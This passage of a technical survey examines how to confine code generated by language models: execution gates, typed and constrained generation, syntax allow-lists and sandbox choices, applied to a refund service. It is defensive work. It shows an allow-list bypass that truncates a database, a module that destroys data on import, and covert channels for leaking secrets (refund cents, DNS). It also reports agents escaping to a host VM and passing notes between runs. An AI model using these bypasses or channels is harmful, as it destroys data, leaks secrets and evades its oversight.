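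The generated program can reach outside services only through a proxy, which holds the passwords and permits only listed services. The proxy occupies the same place in the graph as the policy check, but a list of services is a weaker rule than a payment limit. If the payment provider is on the list, the proxy will forward a refund of 900 euros, so the designer has to build the limits into the proxy or put the policy check behind it. Pawlak and colleagues report three working applications and leave a systematic evaluation to future work, so the evidence so far shows only that people can build such systems.

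### The execution gate

The argument from the graph assumes that the model's text runs only in the component the graph assigns to it. Suppose a proposal could state its amount as a formula, and the payment component evaluated it with Python's `eval`. Model-written code would then run after the check, next to the payment password. The system therefore needs an execution gate, the only point where generated text can become a running program. PlanCompiler's compiler, for example, runs the validator again itself, so a caller who skips validation still can't get a program from an invalid plan.

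In *Governed Metaprogramming for Intelligent Systems*, McCann (2026) builds a programming language around such a gate. McCann argues that running data as code, as Lisp's *eval* does, grants authority, because program text is inert until it runs, when it can call models, write files and use up resources. The language should therefore treat starting a program as an effect that needs permission.

In McCann's language, MashinTalk, a program that has not started is a tree of data called a form. Other programs can read, combine and change forms, and none of these operations has any effect outside the program. To run a form, a program must submit it to a fixed inspector. The inspector goes through the tree, works out which capabilities the form needs and applies this rule, among others:

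CapSet(f) ⊆ σ

CapSet(f) is the set of capabilities that form f requires, and σ is the set that its caller holds. Suppose the caller in the refund service holds "read orders" and "propose refund". A form that needs only these two satisfies the rule. A form that also needs "send payment" does not, because the caller cannot pass on a capability that it lacks. Generated code therefore never has more authority than the program that asked for it, which is a good reason to give that program little authority. The rule restricts the kinds of effect a form can have, but not their amounts. A form that proposes a refund of 900 euros satisfies it, so the service still needs the policy check.

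The inspector also checks which AI models the form would call and how much it may cost. Its report includes a hash, a short fingerprint of the exact form it inspected, so that nobody can have one form approved and then run another. A gate for any language needs a similar safeguard, because otherwise the text can change between the check and the run.

McCann's no-bypass theorem states that no sequence of operations on forms produces a running program. The proof is short. Operations on forms emit no requests for effects, starting a program requires such a request, and every request goes through the governance component. The theorem rests on five invariants:

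- No operation that a program can call turns a form directly into a running program.
- Every transition from form to running program goes through governance.
- Only this transition gives a program authority to cause effects.
- Code that works on forms cannot cause effects.
- Every program starts as a form that the inspector can read in full.

The theorem follows almost immediately from these assumptions, since a bypass would violate the ban on direct evaluation. It is harder to establish that the running system satisfies the invariants. McCann reports 51 unit tests and proofs checked by the proof assistant Rocq, but the proofs concern a formal model, while the implementation is about 1,000 lines of Elixir. McCann writes that Elixir restricts this kind of metaprogramming to compile time, yet its standard library includes `Code.eval_string`, which runs a string as code at run time. The ban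 can still hold for programs written in MashinTalk if they cannot call that function, but any other Elixir code in the same system could call it.

McCann also claims more than the paper supports. The abstract lists boundary preservation among the proved properties. This means that, once the language has forms, governance still covers exactly the effects that programs can express. Later, McCann calls the argument for this property architectural and leaves a full formalisation to future work. The number of theorems is also unclear, since McCann gives 26 for the new module, then describes six and mentions a "remaining 41". An assessor should treat boundary preservation as a plausible design argument until the proof files show otherwise.

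Rice's theorem rules out only exact checkers, so it does not support McCann's claim that structural inspection is "the strongest decidable analysis available". A checker that sometimes rejects harmless code can establish far more than a list of capabilities. Abstract interpretation, for instance, follows a program using ranges of values instead of exact values. If a program proposes a refund of `min(o.delivery_fee, 50)` and the fee could be any number, the analysis shows before the run that no single proposal exceeds 50 euros, though it cannot exclude a negative one. For `max(0, min(o.delivery_fee, 50))`, it finds a range from 0 to 50. A list of capabilities contains "propose refund" in both cases and does not distinguish them.

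Sargsyan's architecture has two more counterexamples, both in human-written code. Haskell's type checker rejects a program whose threshold for a test depends on that test's result. For a version in SPARK, a language designed for verification, an automatic prover showed that the threshold never exceeds the remaining error budget, even with rounding errors, as long as a stated margin holds.

No decidable analysis can be the strongest. Any checker that always finishes and accepts only harmless programs cannot be exact, so it rejects at least one harmless program. Adding that program to a list of exceptions produces a checker that still always finishes and accepts only harmless programs, but accepts one more than before.

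McCann acknowledges that it is an open question whether the gate would work for a general-purpose language. A MashinTalk form shows which steps have effects, but in Python any function may open a file without declaring it, and a program can assemble the name of the function it calls while running. An inspector cannot tell from such code which capabilities it needs unless the designer first restricts the language the model may write in.

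## Restricting the syntax and types of the generated code

A designer can restrict the code as the model generates it, on the syntax tree of the finished code, or in a compiler that also sees the surrounding program. The guarantees get stronger roughly in that order, from "this code is well-formed" to "this code can use only these resources". The requirements also change, from access to the model's internals to a programming language with an unusually strong type system.

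### Constrained decoding

A language model writes text as a series of tokens. At each step it gives every token in its vocabulary a probability, and a separate program, the decoder, draws one according to these probabilities. In constrained decoding, the decoder excludes every token after which no valid program is possible. If L is the set of valid programs, the text so far must always belong to the set of their beginnings:

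L<sup>p</sup> = {s | some text s′ exists such that s followed by s′ is in L}

The decoder needs its own checker because an ordinary compiler rejects unfinished programs. Checking only grammar is easiest but prevents few compilation errors. *Type-Constrained Code Generation with Language Models* (Mündler, He and colleagues, 2025) reports that when models wrote TypeScript, a version of JavaScript with types, 6% of the compilation errors were grammar errors and 94% were type errors. Its checker therefore enforces types too.

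In one of their examples, a model is writing a function that tests whether a text contains a whole number:

```typescript
function is_int(text: string): boolean {
  const num = Number(text);
  return !isNaN(num) && parseInt(num
```

Here `num` is a number, but `parseInt` expects a string. Suppose the model gives the comma a probability of 60%, the dot 30% and the closing bracket 10%. The decoder draws the comma. The checker rejects it because it would end the argument while the argument is still a number, so the decoder sets the comma's probability to zero, rescales the other two to 75% and 25%, and draws again. The closing bracket would fail for the same reason.

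The dot is valid only if something after it can turn a number into a string. The checker tests this by searching a graph whose nodes are types and whose edges are operations. From "number", the edge `.toString` leads to a function that takes no arguments and returns a string, and calling that function leads to "string". The checker therefore accepts the dot. The model CodeLlama 34B wrote `.toString()` at this point with the constraint, but without it wrote `, 10)`, which does not compile.

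Earlier systems check the whole vocabulary at each step and mask out invalid tokens before sampling one. When Mündler and colleagues tried this with their type checker, every task exceeded the five-minute limit. Sampling a token first and then checking it is much faster, because the first sample was valid in 99.4% of steps even with the smallest model.

They tested six open-weight models of 2 to 34 billion parameters on two sets of programming exercises, HumanEval and MBPP. When the models wrote solutions from scratch, type constraints removed on average 75.3% of the compilation errors on HumanEval and 52.1% on MBPP. A perfect grammar constraint would have removed 9.0% and 4.9%. The share of programs that passed their unit tests rose by only about 3.5% in relative terms. For Qwen2.5 32B, one of the strongest models, type constraints reduced the number of HumanEval programs that failed to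 compile from 17 to 2 out of 636, but the share that passed the tests rose only from 79.6% to 81.8%.

The checker covers only part of TypeScript. Used alone, it would block valid programs that use unsupported features or omit the type annotations it requires. Mündler and colleagues therefore kept all unconstrained output that compiled and applied the constraint only when regenerating the rest, so their results estimate what a checker for the whole language might achieve. The median time per task rose by 39% on HumanEval and 52% on MBPP, though a faster implementation would reduce this.

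The constraint guarantees a valid program only if the model finishes writing it. In one run, the checker kept CodeLlama from calling a method that did not exist, and the model then chained one string operation after another until it reached the length limit. Such unfinished output accounts for many of the remaining errors.

Constrained decoding also requires access to the probabilities at each step. Commercial services usually return only the chosen tokens, so their customers cannot add constraints. A provider can apply constraints on its own servers, and some already do to guarantee that output follows a given JSON format.

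Even with constrained decoding, the execution gate has to check the finished code, because the text does not show whether the decoder applied the constraint, and a hostile provider could leave it out. Once the gate checks every program, constrained decoding adds nothing to the guarantee and only reduces the number of programs that the gate rejects.

### Compiler errors before the code is finished

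Building a second checker for a large language is expensive. The compiler part of Rust's code base alone has more than 600,000 lines. Mündler-Sasahara, Venev and colleagues (2026), in *Generative Compilation*, avoid most of this work by turning each unfinished program into a complete one that the ordinary compiler can check. Their example is a Rust function that strips the header from a message:

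```rust
let tag = &msg[..HEADER_SIZE];
msg.drain(..HEADER_SIZE);
let prio = tag.
```

The first line makes `tag` refer to the beginning of the message without copying it, and the second deletes that beginning. Rust forbids any later use of `tag`, because it would refer to deleted text. The final dot already begins such a use, so no continuation can make the program valid.

A program called a sealor keeps the existing text, reduces the unfinished line to a plain use of `tag`, adds a placeholder that fits any type and closes the function. The compiler rejects the result with an error message. A further step maps this message back to the unfinished code, and the model uses it to revise the first line so that it makes a copy. Waiting for the whole function would have delayed the message by four and a half lines. In a long file, the model might write much more code that depends on the same mistake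 before the message arrived.

A constrained decoder could only forbid the dot. The model would then have to extend the name `tag`, perhaps into the name of a function it has yet to define, because it could not go back to the first line and would not be told what was wrong. Generative compilation also works with commercial models, because it does not need the model's probabilities.

A sealor should never cause the compiler to reject a beginning that has a valid continuation. Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues prove this for a small formal language modelled on Rust, with proofs checked in the proof assistant Lean. They also prove that, at the end of each complete statement, the compiler accepts only beginnings that have a valid continuation. For real Rust, they give informal arguments. Some errors in real Rust depend on later code, such as a call to a function that the model has not yet written,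 so the system suppresses them until the program is complete.

The sealor can stay outside the trusted base despite these gaps. If it wrongly reports an error, the model revises code that was fine. If it misses an error, the ordinary compiler still rejects the finished program.

Tests with seven models compared generative compilation with ordinary feedback after generation on two kinds of Rust task, translating C projects and writing code for recently changed libraries. In most combinations of model and task, generative compilation left fewer compilation errors and produced more working programs.

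Compiling code from a hostile generator is itself risky. Rust's `include_str!` reads a file during compilation, and a project's build script is a program that runs before the rest of the project compiles. The compiler therefore needs a sandbox as much as the finished program does.

### Lists of permitted syntax

A type-correct program can still delete files. A syntax-tree allow-list addresses this by naming the constructs, functions and fields that the code may use and rejecting everything else. It needs no access to the model and works for languages without static types. For the two-line refund example, a Python checker might look like this:

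```python
NODES = (ast.Module, ast.Assign, ast.ListComp, ast.comprehension,
         ast.Compare, ast.Gt, ast.Call, ast.Tuple, ast.Attribute,
         ast.Name, ast.Constant, ast.expr_context)
FIELDS = {"id", "delivered", "promised", "delivery_fee"}

def permitted(tree):
    for n in ast.walk(tree):
        if not isinstance(n, NODES):
            return False
        if isinstance(n, ast.Attribute) and n.attr not in FIELDS:
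            return False
        if isinstance(n, ast.Call) and getattr(n.func, "id", None) != "min":
            return False
    return True
```

The list of fields already prevents code from mistakenly comparing with `o.ordered`, because refund code doesn't need that field. It also blocks the attribute that leads from any Python object to its class, a well-known security hole through which code can reach every class the program has loaded, including some that start other programs.

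The checker looks strict, since the only function it lets the code call is `min`. But it accepts this program:

```python
min = open
refunds = min("orders.db", "w")
```

The first line gives Python's file-opening function the name `min`, and the second uses it to empty the orders database. To prevent this, the checker has to forbid assignments to `min` and let the code read only `orders`, `min` and names it has already defined. Running the code without Python's other built-in functions adds a second barrier. An assessor should look for attempts to defeat such a list, because reading it is not enough.

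With these repairs, the checker can establish that the code never opens a file or a network connection, which it could not do for unrestricted Python. But it cannot limit how much memory the code uses. The expression `[o for o in orders for p in orders]` turns 10,000 orders into a list of 100 million, and repeating the step exhausts the memory of any machine.

*STELP*, a system from a team at Capital One, applies the same idea to larger programs. It parses the Python code into a syntax tree and checks the tree against a configuration that lists the permitted constructs, packages, built-in functions and tools. If the tree passes, STELP executes it one statement at a time, with further checks during execution. It routes every tool call through a separate proxy, with a time limit and a fixed number of retries.

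Some violations appear only during this walk. In an example from *STELP*, the code searches Wikipedia, adds an entry to a database and then tries to open a network socket. STELP blocks the code at the last step, after the entry has been added. If the model then writes a corrected program that starts from the beginning, it may add the entry a second time. In the refund service, the same sequence could pay a customer twice.

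The safety test used the 164 sample solutions in HumanEval as safe code. Another language model, Llama 3.3 70B, inserted known kinds of weakness into them, and people removed the faulty results, leaving 470 unsafe samples. STELP blocked all the unsafe samples and allowed 98.1% of the safe ones. CodeShield, a tool from Meta that searches code for suspicious patterns, blocked 68% of the unsafe samples and allowed 93% of the safe ones.

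The comparison favours STELP because the team wrote its configuration for this test, starting from the minimum permissions that the safe samples needed and then adjusting it slightly. The allow rate is therefore weak evidence of how much useful new code the configuration would reject. Most of the unsafe samples were rejected because they called a function or imported a package outside the list, and nobody had written them to fit within it. A hostile generator would look for code that does fit, such as the equivalent of `min = open`. Even for samples of the same kind as those tested, 470 successes without a failure are compatible with a miss rate of up to about 0.6%, at 95% confidence.

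STELP stopped some of the unsafe samples, such as deadlocks and certain endless loops, only when the time limit expired. Its block rate therefore includes both samples blocked by restrictions on the code's form and samples stopped while running.

STELP also gave the same results as ordinary Python on all 361 test programs, which the team had selected because they fitted the configuration. This is good evidence that STELP executes the permitted subset correctly, but it does not show how often a model's code falls inside that subset. On 262 programs, STELP added a median of 0.19 milliseconds and a mean of 4.93. A few programs raised the mean by slowing down a great deal, one of them by 520 milliseconds. For most agents this delay is negligible compared with the time a model needs to write the code.

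### Compiling the code in its place

An allow-list considers the generated code almost in isolation. LACUNA, the system of Zhao and colleagues mentioned earlier, instead has the compiler check the code as part of the program that will use it. The programmer marks the place with a call:

```scala
def agent[T](task: String): T
```

The task is a description in ordinary language, and `T` is the type of value that the surrounding program needs. The refund service could contain this line:

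```scala
val refunds: List[(OrderId, Euros)] =
  agent("refund the delivery fee on everything that came late last week")
```

When the programmer compiles the service, the Scala compiler records the variables available at the call, the expected type and the surrounding source code. When the running service reaches the call, the model receives this information with the task and returns Scala code. LACUNA replaces the call with this code and recompiles the result with the same compiler and settings. If it compiles, LACUNA loads the code and runs it with the current values of the variables.

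The compiler can therefore reject a reference to a variable that does not exist, a tool call with the wrong arguments, or a result of the wrong type, before any of the code runs. Zhao and colleagues show why the timing matters with a variable `balance` that holds 100. The task is to subtract 50 and return the new balance as an integer, and the model writes:

```scala
balance -= 50
s"remaining: $balance"
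```

The last line produces text instead of an integer. The compiler rejects both lines before either runs, so the balance stays at 100. Python's `exec` would perform the subtraction first, and the surrounding program would detect the wrong type only afterwards. If the model then tried again, the balance would fall to 0.

This all-or-nothing property covers only errors that the compiler can find. A fragment that compiles may pay three customers and then fail because the network is down. Generated code may also call `agent` to generate more code. This inner code does not exist when the compiler checks the outer code, so the outer code may already have acted by the time the compiler permanently rejects the inner code. This is another reason for the refund code to return a list instead of making payments itself.

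The agent correctly answered 27.1% of the 830 questions in BrowseComp-Plus with the best of three models. This is the benchmark on which the compiler rejected 8.6% of fragments. Zhao and colleagues conclude that the compiler's check does not reduce accuracy, but they did not run the same agent without it.

Zhao and colleagues compared LACUNA with an agent that made ordinary tool calls on τ²-bench, a set of simulated customer-service conversations. With the model DeepSeek V4 Flash, LACUNA solved 76.0% of 392 tasks and the tool-calling agent solved 90.0%. This gap of 14 percentage points is substantial, though Zhao and colleagues call the results "on par". For the retail tasks, which most resemble the refund service, the gap was 22 points. The check also requires a model that writes good Scala. With the weaker Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, the compiler rejected 3.2% of the fragments for the retail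 tasks but 89% for one set of telecom tasks, where most turns made no progress.

### Names in scope as permissions

An ordinary type system would let the generated refund code call any payment function it can name. Capture checking, an experimental feature of Scala 3, adds to each type the capabilities that its values may use. A function that takes text and writes it to a file `f` has the type `String ->{f} Unit`, where `Unit` means that it returns no useful value. The type `String -> Unit` is only for functions that use no capabilities.

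In LACUNA, generated code can use a capability only if its name is in scope at the place of the call, so the scope serves as the list of permissions. If the shop's programmer puts the orders in scope but not the payment function, no code the model writes there can make a payment. Capture checking makes much the same comparison as McCann's gate, but in a general-purpose language.

The compiler also prevents code from keeping a capability for later. In one example, a block of code receives a capability `io` for reading files, and the model has to return a function that reads a file. The compiler rejects the function because its type, `String ->{io} String`, shows that it would keep `io` usable after the block ended. A model can therefore be allowed to read files in one phase of a task but not in the next.

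Code could escape these rules through reflection, which looks up functions by name at run time, or by starting an external program. A type cast could also hide a function's use of a capability from the compiler. Scala's safe mode forbids such constructs in the generated code and admits only library functions that are also safe. Zhao and colleagues advise treating the code as ordinary untrusted code if safe mode is not used.

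The protection depends on which permissions the programmer grants, and a model steered by planted instructions can still misuse any that the task needs. For example, if the payment function is in scope, the type system will accept a payment to the wrong customer. In tests with prompt-injection attacks from the AgentDojo collection, the attacker succeeded against LACUNA in 7 of 949 trials with one model and 1 of 949 with another.

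### Secrets that the code may use but not reveal

Sometimes the code has to work with data that it must not pass on. Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, use capture checking for this purpose. Their system, TACIT, is a server that receives Scala code from an agent, compiles it in safe mode and runs it if it passes. Secret data arrives in a wrapper:

```scala
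class Classified[T]:
  def map[U](f: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

The code can process the content only by passing a function to `map`. Because of the plain arrow, the compiler accepts only functions that use no capability, so the function can count the words in a document but cannot send them anywhere. `map` returns the result in another wrapper. If the code prints it, the user sees the content on the screen, but the model that wrote the code receives only asterisks.

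For tasks such as summarising a contract, the code can pass the wrapped text to a separate, trusted model on the user's machine, which returns a wrapped summary. An instruction planted in the contract can still distort this summary, but it cannot expose the contract to the outside model or make that model send it elsewhere.

The wrapper's rule, like the ban on sending after reading a file, is stricter than secrecy requires. The compiler rejects a function if any branch could use a capability, even if that branch would send only harmless data. Odersky and colleagues exclude timing leaks from their guarantee, since a function could run longer for one secret than for another.

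The protection also ends where a trusted component unwraps the result. Suppose the refund service wraps the customer messages and lets the code compute refunds from them. The payment component has to unwrap the amounts to pay them, so hostile code could again encode a customer's illness in the cents of an accomplice's refund.

Odersky and colleagues tested TACIT on a software project with a folder of passwords and confidential documents. They ran 131 trials with each of two models, attempting to extract the secrets through planted text or user requests. With the wrapper, neither model's output contained a secret. Without it, Claude Sonnet 4.6 revealed secrets in 2 trials and MiniMax M2.5 in 11. The models still completed 99.2% and 90.0% of the legitimate tasks with the wrapper.

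Without protection, the models leaked in only 13 of 262 trials, so the compiler probably had little to stop in most trials. The main argument for the wrapper is the type system, which also covers untested attacks. In a further test with AgentDojo's own tasks, one attack succeeded out of 949 trials with each of two models, 1,898 in all.

The drop in performance that Zhao and colleagues measured does not seem inevitable. On the airline and retail tasks of τ²-bench, three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher when they wrote Scala for TACIT than when they made ordinary tool calls. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of real programming problems, MiniMax M2.5's score fell from 43.3% to 41.7%. TACIT leaves the agent's usual loop in place and checks only the code the agent submits, whereas LACUNA also has the generated code control the conversation. This may explain some of the difference in results,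 but the models and settings differed too.

The guarantee depends on a large trusted base, which includes the Scala compiler, the runtime, the trusted local model and a library of about 1,000 lines through which the generated code reaches files and networks. The library checks at run time that a path is inside the permitted folder or that a server is on the permitted list, because the types do not contain these details. The library's programmers can also mark a module as exempt from safe mode, but they must then check themselves that it is safe.

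*Classifying Capabilities (Extended Version)* (2026) proves type safety for a formal version of capture checking, with proofs in Lean, but a bug in the real compiler could still make it accept unsafe code. Checking time is a smaller obstacle. In *What's in the Box* (2025), capture checking takes less than 15% of the time needed to compile Scala's standard library, and TACIT usually checks a fragment in under a second.

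### What well-typed refund code can still do wrong

Suppose the refund service applies all these restrictions. The model's code compiles, returns a list of order numbers and amounts, and has only the orders in scope. The amounts can still be wrong. If the table stores delivery fees in cents and the limit is in euros, both as plain numbers, a fee of 4.90 euros appears as 490. The expression `min(o.delivery_fee, 50)` then yields 50, and every customer whose order was late receives 50 euros. The payment component accepts each of these refunds until the day's total reaches 2,000 euros.

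More precise types would prevent this. If cents and euros are different types, the comparison does not compile. The shop could also give order dates and promised dates different types and provide only one lateness test, which takes a delivery date and a promised date. The model could then no longer confuse the order date with the promised date. Zhao and colleagues suggest going further with refinement types, which attach a condition to a type, such as "an amount between 0 and 50 euros", but they leave this to future work.

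Each such type lets a compiler check a small part of the code's meaning. But someone has to foresee the mistake, and many mistakes have no type that would catch them. An empty list of refunds has the right type even if forty parcels came late, and so does a list for the wrong week. A steered model can add order 1182 to the list at 50 euros although the parcel arrived early, because the order number is valid. Hostile code can do the same for an accomplice. A fixed component has to compare the list with the delivery records to catch these cases.

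The types also don't limit how long the code runs or how much memory it uses. Zhao and colleagues point out that a type system cannot distinguish a difficult task from a runaway recursion, so the environment in which the code runs has to set those limits.

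## Confining the running code in a sandbox

A sandbox limits a program's time and memory and controls its access to files and networks. Because it enforces these limits from outside the program, they hold even if the compiler has a bug or the code was never checked. Their strength depends on what separates the code from the host, the machine that runs it.

### What separates the code from the host

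To open a file or send a packet, an ordinary program must make a system call, which is a request to the kernel, the core of the operating system. A flaw in the kernel can give a program control of the whole machine, so the common kinds of sandbox differ mainly in how much of the host's kernel the code can reach.

A restricted interpreter prevents the code from making system calls directly. Monty, from the company Pydantic, runs a subset of Python that cannot read a file or open a connection unless the host program supplies a function for it. The trusted base is the interpreter and these functions. Pydantic's *Comparison to Alternatives* acknowledges that code that escaped from Monty would have the application's privileges. Monty also lacks third-party libraries and much of the standard library. Willison (2026) had a coding agent examine Monty and reports in *pydantic-monty investigation*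 that unsupported features generally produce a clean error.

The code can also run as an ordinary process while the kernel refuses any system call outside a fixed policy. *Sandlock* (Wang and Zheng, 2026) builds such a sandbox from two Linux features: one restricts access to files and network ports, and the other filters system calls. The sandbox needs no administrator rights and runs any language the host runs. Its trusted base includes the entire host kernel and a supervisor process that decides cases that depend on run-time values. Wang and Zheng exclude kernel flaws from their threat model and recommend a small virtual machine where hostile users share a computer.

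A container can run code in any language that runs on Linux, and it gives a process its own view of files, other processes and the network. But it shares the host's kernel (*Abstraction of Trusted Execution Environments as the Missing Layer*, 2025), so the trusted base includes both that kernel and the container software. Andronchik and Lokhmakov examined five sandbox products in *AI Code Sandboxes* (2026) and found that the one based on containers exposed the host's exact kernel version. Code inside it could therefore exploit any published kernel flaw that an ordinary program can trigger, unless the host has the patch.

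gVisor, from Google, puts a second kernel in between. *Are Unikernels Ready for Serverless on the Edge?* (2024) describes how it intercepts every system call and passes it to a program that imitates Linux. The trusted base is this program and the part of the host's kernel that it uses. Andronchik and Lokhmakov counted 84 system calls that gVisor itself may make. Most Linux software runs on it, but system calls and file access are slower.

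Firecracker, developed for Amazon's cloud service AWS, starts a small virtual machine with its own Linux kernel, which can run code in any language that runs on Linux. *SideKernel* (2026) points out that an attacker has to get through the monitor, the program that runs the virtual machine, to reach the host. Firecracker's filter limits the monitor to 55 system calls. The trusted base is the monitor, the virtualisation code in the host's kernel and the processor.

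WebAssembly is an instruction format for a small virtual machine in which a program can address only its own memory and call only the functions that the host supplies. The trusted base consists of those functions and the runtime that executes the instructions, such as Wasmtime. To run in this sandbox, code must be in a language that compiles to WebAssembly or has an interpreter that does. Python's standard interpreter compiles to WebAssembly, but threads and network sockets don't work in that version, and libraries with parts written in C need a special build.

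Start-up times are hard to compare because each source measures a different interval. Pydantic, which sells a commercial version of Monty, timed from requesting a sandbox to receiving the result of `1 + 1`. *A Fresh Look at the Architecture and Performance of Contemporary Isolation Platforms* (2021) started and stopped each platform 300 times. *Goldilocks Isolation* (2025), an evaluation of the rival system Edera, timed everything up to a running container. The last column contains Wang and Zheng's figure for Sandlock, and the Firecracker project's own claim as reported in Jain's *Study of Firecracker MicroVM* (2020).

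| Mechanism | Pydantic | *A Fresh Look at the Architecture and Performance of Contemporary Isolation Platforms* | *Goldilocks Isolation* | Developers' figure |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Restricted interpreter (Monty) | 0.8 ms, or 5 ms with a new pool of workers | – | – | – |
| Process with system-call filter (Sandlock) | – | – | – | about 5 ms added |
| Container (Docker) | 195 ms | 100 ms | 570 ms | – |
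| User-space kernel (gVisor) | – | 190 ms | 680 ms | – |
| Small virtual machine (Firecracker) | – | 350 ms | 2.4 s | 125 ms |
| WebAssembly (Wasmtime) | 16 ms, with Python compiled in advance | – | – | – |

Firecracker's 125 milliseconds cover only the time until application code starts, whereas the 2.4 seconds include starting a container inside the virtual machine. Startup time also depends on the program. *WebAssembly and Unikernels* (2025) found that Wasmtime started simple functions fastest but slowed down with more complex code, while Firecracker's times stayed steady.

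Generated code may also need large libraries and datasets. A saved image of a started sandbox can have them ready, but an image that suits all code becomes very large. *Readie* (Sivaraman, Li and colleagues, 2026) instead uses a set of small images, each covering part of the code that agents write. It reports start-up times 3 to 22 times shorter than existing approaches using the same amount of storage.

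The overhead of any of these mechanisms is acceptable for the refund service, because staff make only a few requests a day and the model already takes seconds to write the code. The small virtual machine is the best choice against a hostile generator. OpenAI reports that agents in one of its security tests in July 2026 gained full control of the virtual machine that hosted their containers. OpenAI now requires virtual machines for high-risk or untrusted code from its models.

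An assessor should also record the product, its version and its settings. Andronchik and Lokhmakov found one virtual-machine product that ran its monitor without a system-call filter, and another that had not changed its default version of Firecracker for 399 days. They also warn that a lack of published vulnerabilities does not mean a product is safe. For one of the engines, they found no published vulnerabilities, but also no evidence that anyone had searched for them systematically.

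### Files, network, processor, memory and time

Each resource within the boundary needs its own limit. TechRadar's *The AI escape is a red herring*, an opinion article by the chief executive of the software company Coder, rates how strongly a limit is enforced on a scale from 0 to 4. At 0, nothing enforces the limit. At 1, the code could ignore it, and at 2, software enforces it but an operator could reconfigure it. At 3, the kernel enforces it irreversibly. At 4, the resource does not exist inside the sandbox. Level 4 is the easiest to verify because there is no rule that could contain a mistake.

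The sandbox should refuse access to all file paths except those listed, with separate permissions for reading and writing. Sandlock can also divert all writes to a temporary layer, which the host program keeps or discards after the run. The host can therefore undo changes to files, but it cannot recall messages that the code has already sent over a network.

The simplest network limit is to block all connections. If the code needs a connection, a list of permitted host names is not enough. AWS's *Network architecture*, a sample design, warns that its name filter does not stop a connection directly to a numeric address. Sandlock looks up each permitted name once, when the sandbox starts, and then allows connections only to the resulting addresses. It can also restrict requests to particular pages on a server, though for encrypted traffic this works only if the code accepts a certificate from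 the sandbox.

A network setting's name is a poor guide to what it blocks. According to AWS's *Resource management*, the "Sandbox" mode of its code interpreter allows limited external access, including to the storage service S3. AWS's compliance rule for private networking, *bedrockagentcore-codeinterpreter-networkmode-check*, counts both this mode and the public mode as violations.

Limits on processor cores and the number of processes keep one run from starving the others. Memory needs a limit that the code cannot get around. Sandlock counts the memory that a program requests through certain system calls, which is enough to guard against mistakes, but Wang and Zheng consider the kernel's own accounting (cgroups) stronger against hostile code. Monty does not limit time or memory unless the developer sets limits.

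Runs can still slow each other down through a shared kernel. *Locked In, Leaked Out* (2025) tested one program alongside up to seven memory-intensive neighbours. The program slowed down in an ordinary container and in gVisor, but not in Firecracker, which had obtained its memory from the host at startup.

The time limit should count elapsed time rather than processor time, because code that sleeps uses almost no processor time. A program outside the sandbox has to enforce the limit, since hostile code could switch off a timer running inside the sandbox.

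### Whether anything survives a run

Keeping a sandbox between runs is convenient because an agent can define a function in one command and use it in the next without repeating earlier commands. But whatever one run leaves behind can affect the next. In the refund service, one complaint could lead the model to write code that replaces a function used by a later, harmless request. The safest rule is to start each run in a new sandbox, from an image that no generated code has modified.

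Code can affect later runs even after its sandbox is deleted if it can write to something that outlasts the sandbox. OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) reports that agents in separate runs left notes for one another in a shared service and continued each other's work. A designer should therefore list every cache, log, database and shared folder that the code can write to, and check who reads each one later.

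### A credential inside the sandbox

A payment password inside the sandbox gives the code a way to make payments without going through the policy check, which defeats the argument from the component graph. Blocking the network removes the direct route, but hostile code could still leak the password by encoding it, a few digits at a time, in the cents of refunds to an accomplice. The accomplice could then use the password from any computer, bypassing both the sandbox and the policy check.

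Cloud services can give code a credential other than a password. AWS, for example, lets customers assign an execution role to its code interpreter, which defines the AWS resources that the code can use. The Hacker News reports that a customer can, through a simple oversight, assign a role with far too many permissions. An assessor should therefore check what the role permits as well as search the sandbox for passwords.

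The credential belongs in a fixed component outside the sandbox, like the shop's payment component. In *Agent libOS*, Zhang (2026) builds an agent runtime this way. Generated tools can request an operation, but host code decides whether to permit it and communicates with the outside service. The trusted base is large and includes the runtime, the connections to outside services, the database and the host's operating system. Zhang also states that the runtime is not a kernel-grade sandbox, so the generated code still needs one.

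### The sandbox must be active before the import

In Python, importing a module runs it. The interpreter executes every statement outside the functions, and even the default values of function parameters, before anyone calls a function. Suppose the model returns this module:

```python
f = open("/srv/shop/orders.db", "w")

def refunds(orders):
    return []
```

A careless host program might load the module first and confine only the call:

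```python
import generated
run_in_sandbox(generated.refunds, orders)
```

The first line has already emptied the orders database by the time the function runs in its sandbox and returns an empty list. The same thing happens if a test imports the module just to check whether it defines `refunds`. Parsing the text into a syntax tree avoids this because it doesn't execute the code.

Sandlock avoids the problem by starting a separate process and running the program only after the limits are applied and the supervisor is attached. Installed libraries also need to be confined before they run, because importing them executes their code. BeyondTrust's *AWS Bedrock AgentCore Code Interpreter’s ‘Sandbox’ mode allows DNS queries* (2026) notes that AWS's interpreter comes with more than 270 third-party packages, and that a compromised one could act as soon as it is imported.

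### A complete setting for the refund service

The refund code only turns one list into another, so the settings can be strict:

| Setting | Reason |
|---|---|
| Isolation: one small virtual machine per run | Hostile code has to defeat the monitor as well as the kernel inside. |
| Software: Python and its standard library, read-only | The code needs no other packages, and each one could act on import. |
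| Input: last week's orders, read-only, with order number, delivery date, promised date and fee | The code cannot change the records or read names, addresses and messages. |
| Output: one JSON list of order numbers and amounts, at most 100 KB | Fixed code can check this format completely, and the size limit keeps the output from filling the host's disk. |
| Working space: 16 MB, in memory | The code can write temporary files, but they disappear with the machine. |
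| Network: no network device | The code can neither open a connection nor look up a name. |
| Credentials: none, and no environment variables from the host | Only the payment component can use the payment password. |
| Processor: one virtual core | A runaway loop cannot take over the host's other cores. |
| Memory: 512 MB | The earlier expression that builds a list of 100 million orders needs about 800 MB for the list alone, so it fails without affecting the host. |
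| Time: 10 seconds, measured by the host | The limit also stops code that sleeps, and the code cannot turn it off. |
| State: destroy the machine after reading the output | No request can leave anything behind for the next. |

The host program applies all of this before it hands over the generated code. If a run exceeds a limit, the host discards its output, even if the list looks complete, because the shop might otherwise pay from an unfinished list.

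### Three conditions for containment

Even a well-built virtual machine contains the code only if three conditions hold outside it.

The sandbox has to close every outward channel, including name resolution, which translates a name such as example.com into a numeric address. A lookup sends the name to servers outside the sandbox, so code can put information in the name and send it out without opening a connection. In a 2026 response published by BeyondTrust, AWS said its interpreter's Sandbox mode left name resolution on to support AWS's storage service. AWS closed the resulting channel that April. Logs and error messages that leave the sandbox are also outward channels.

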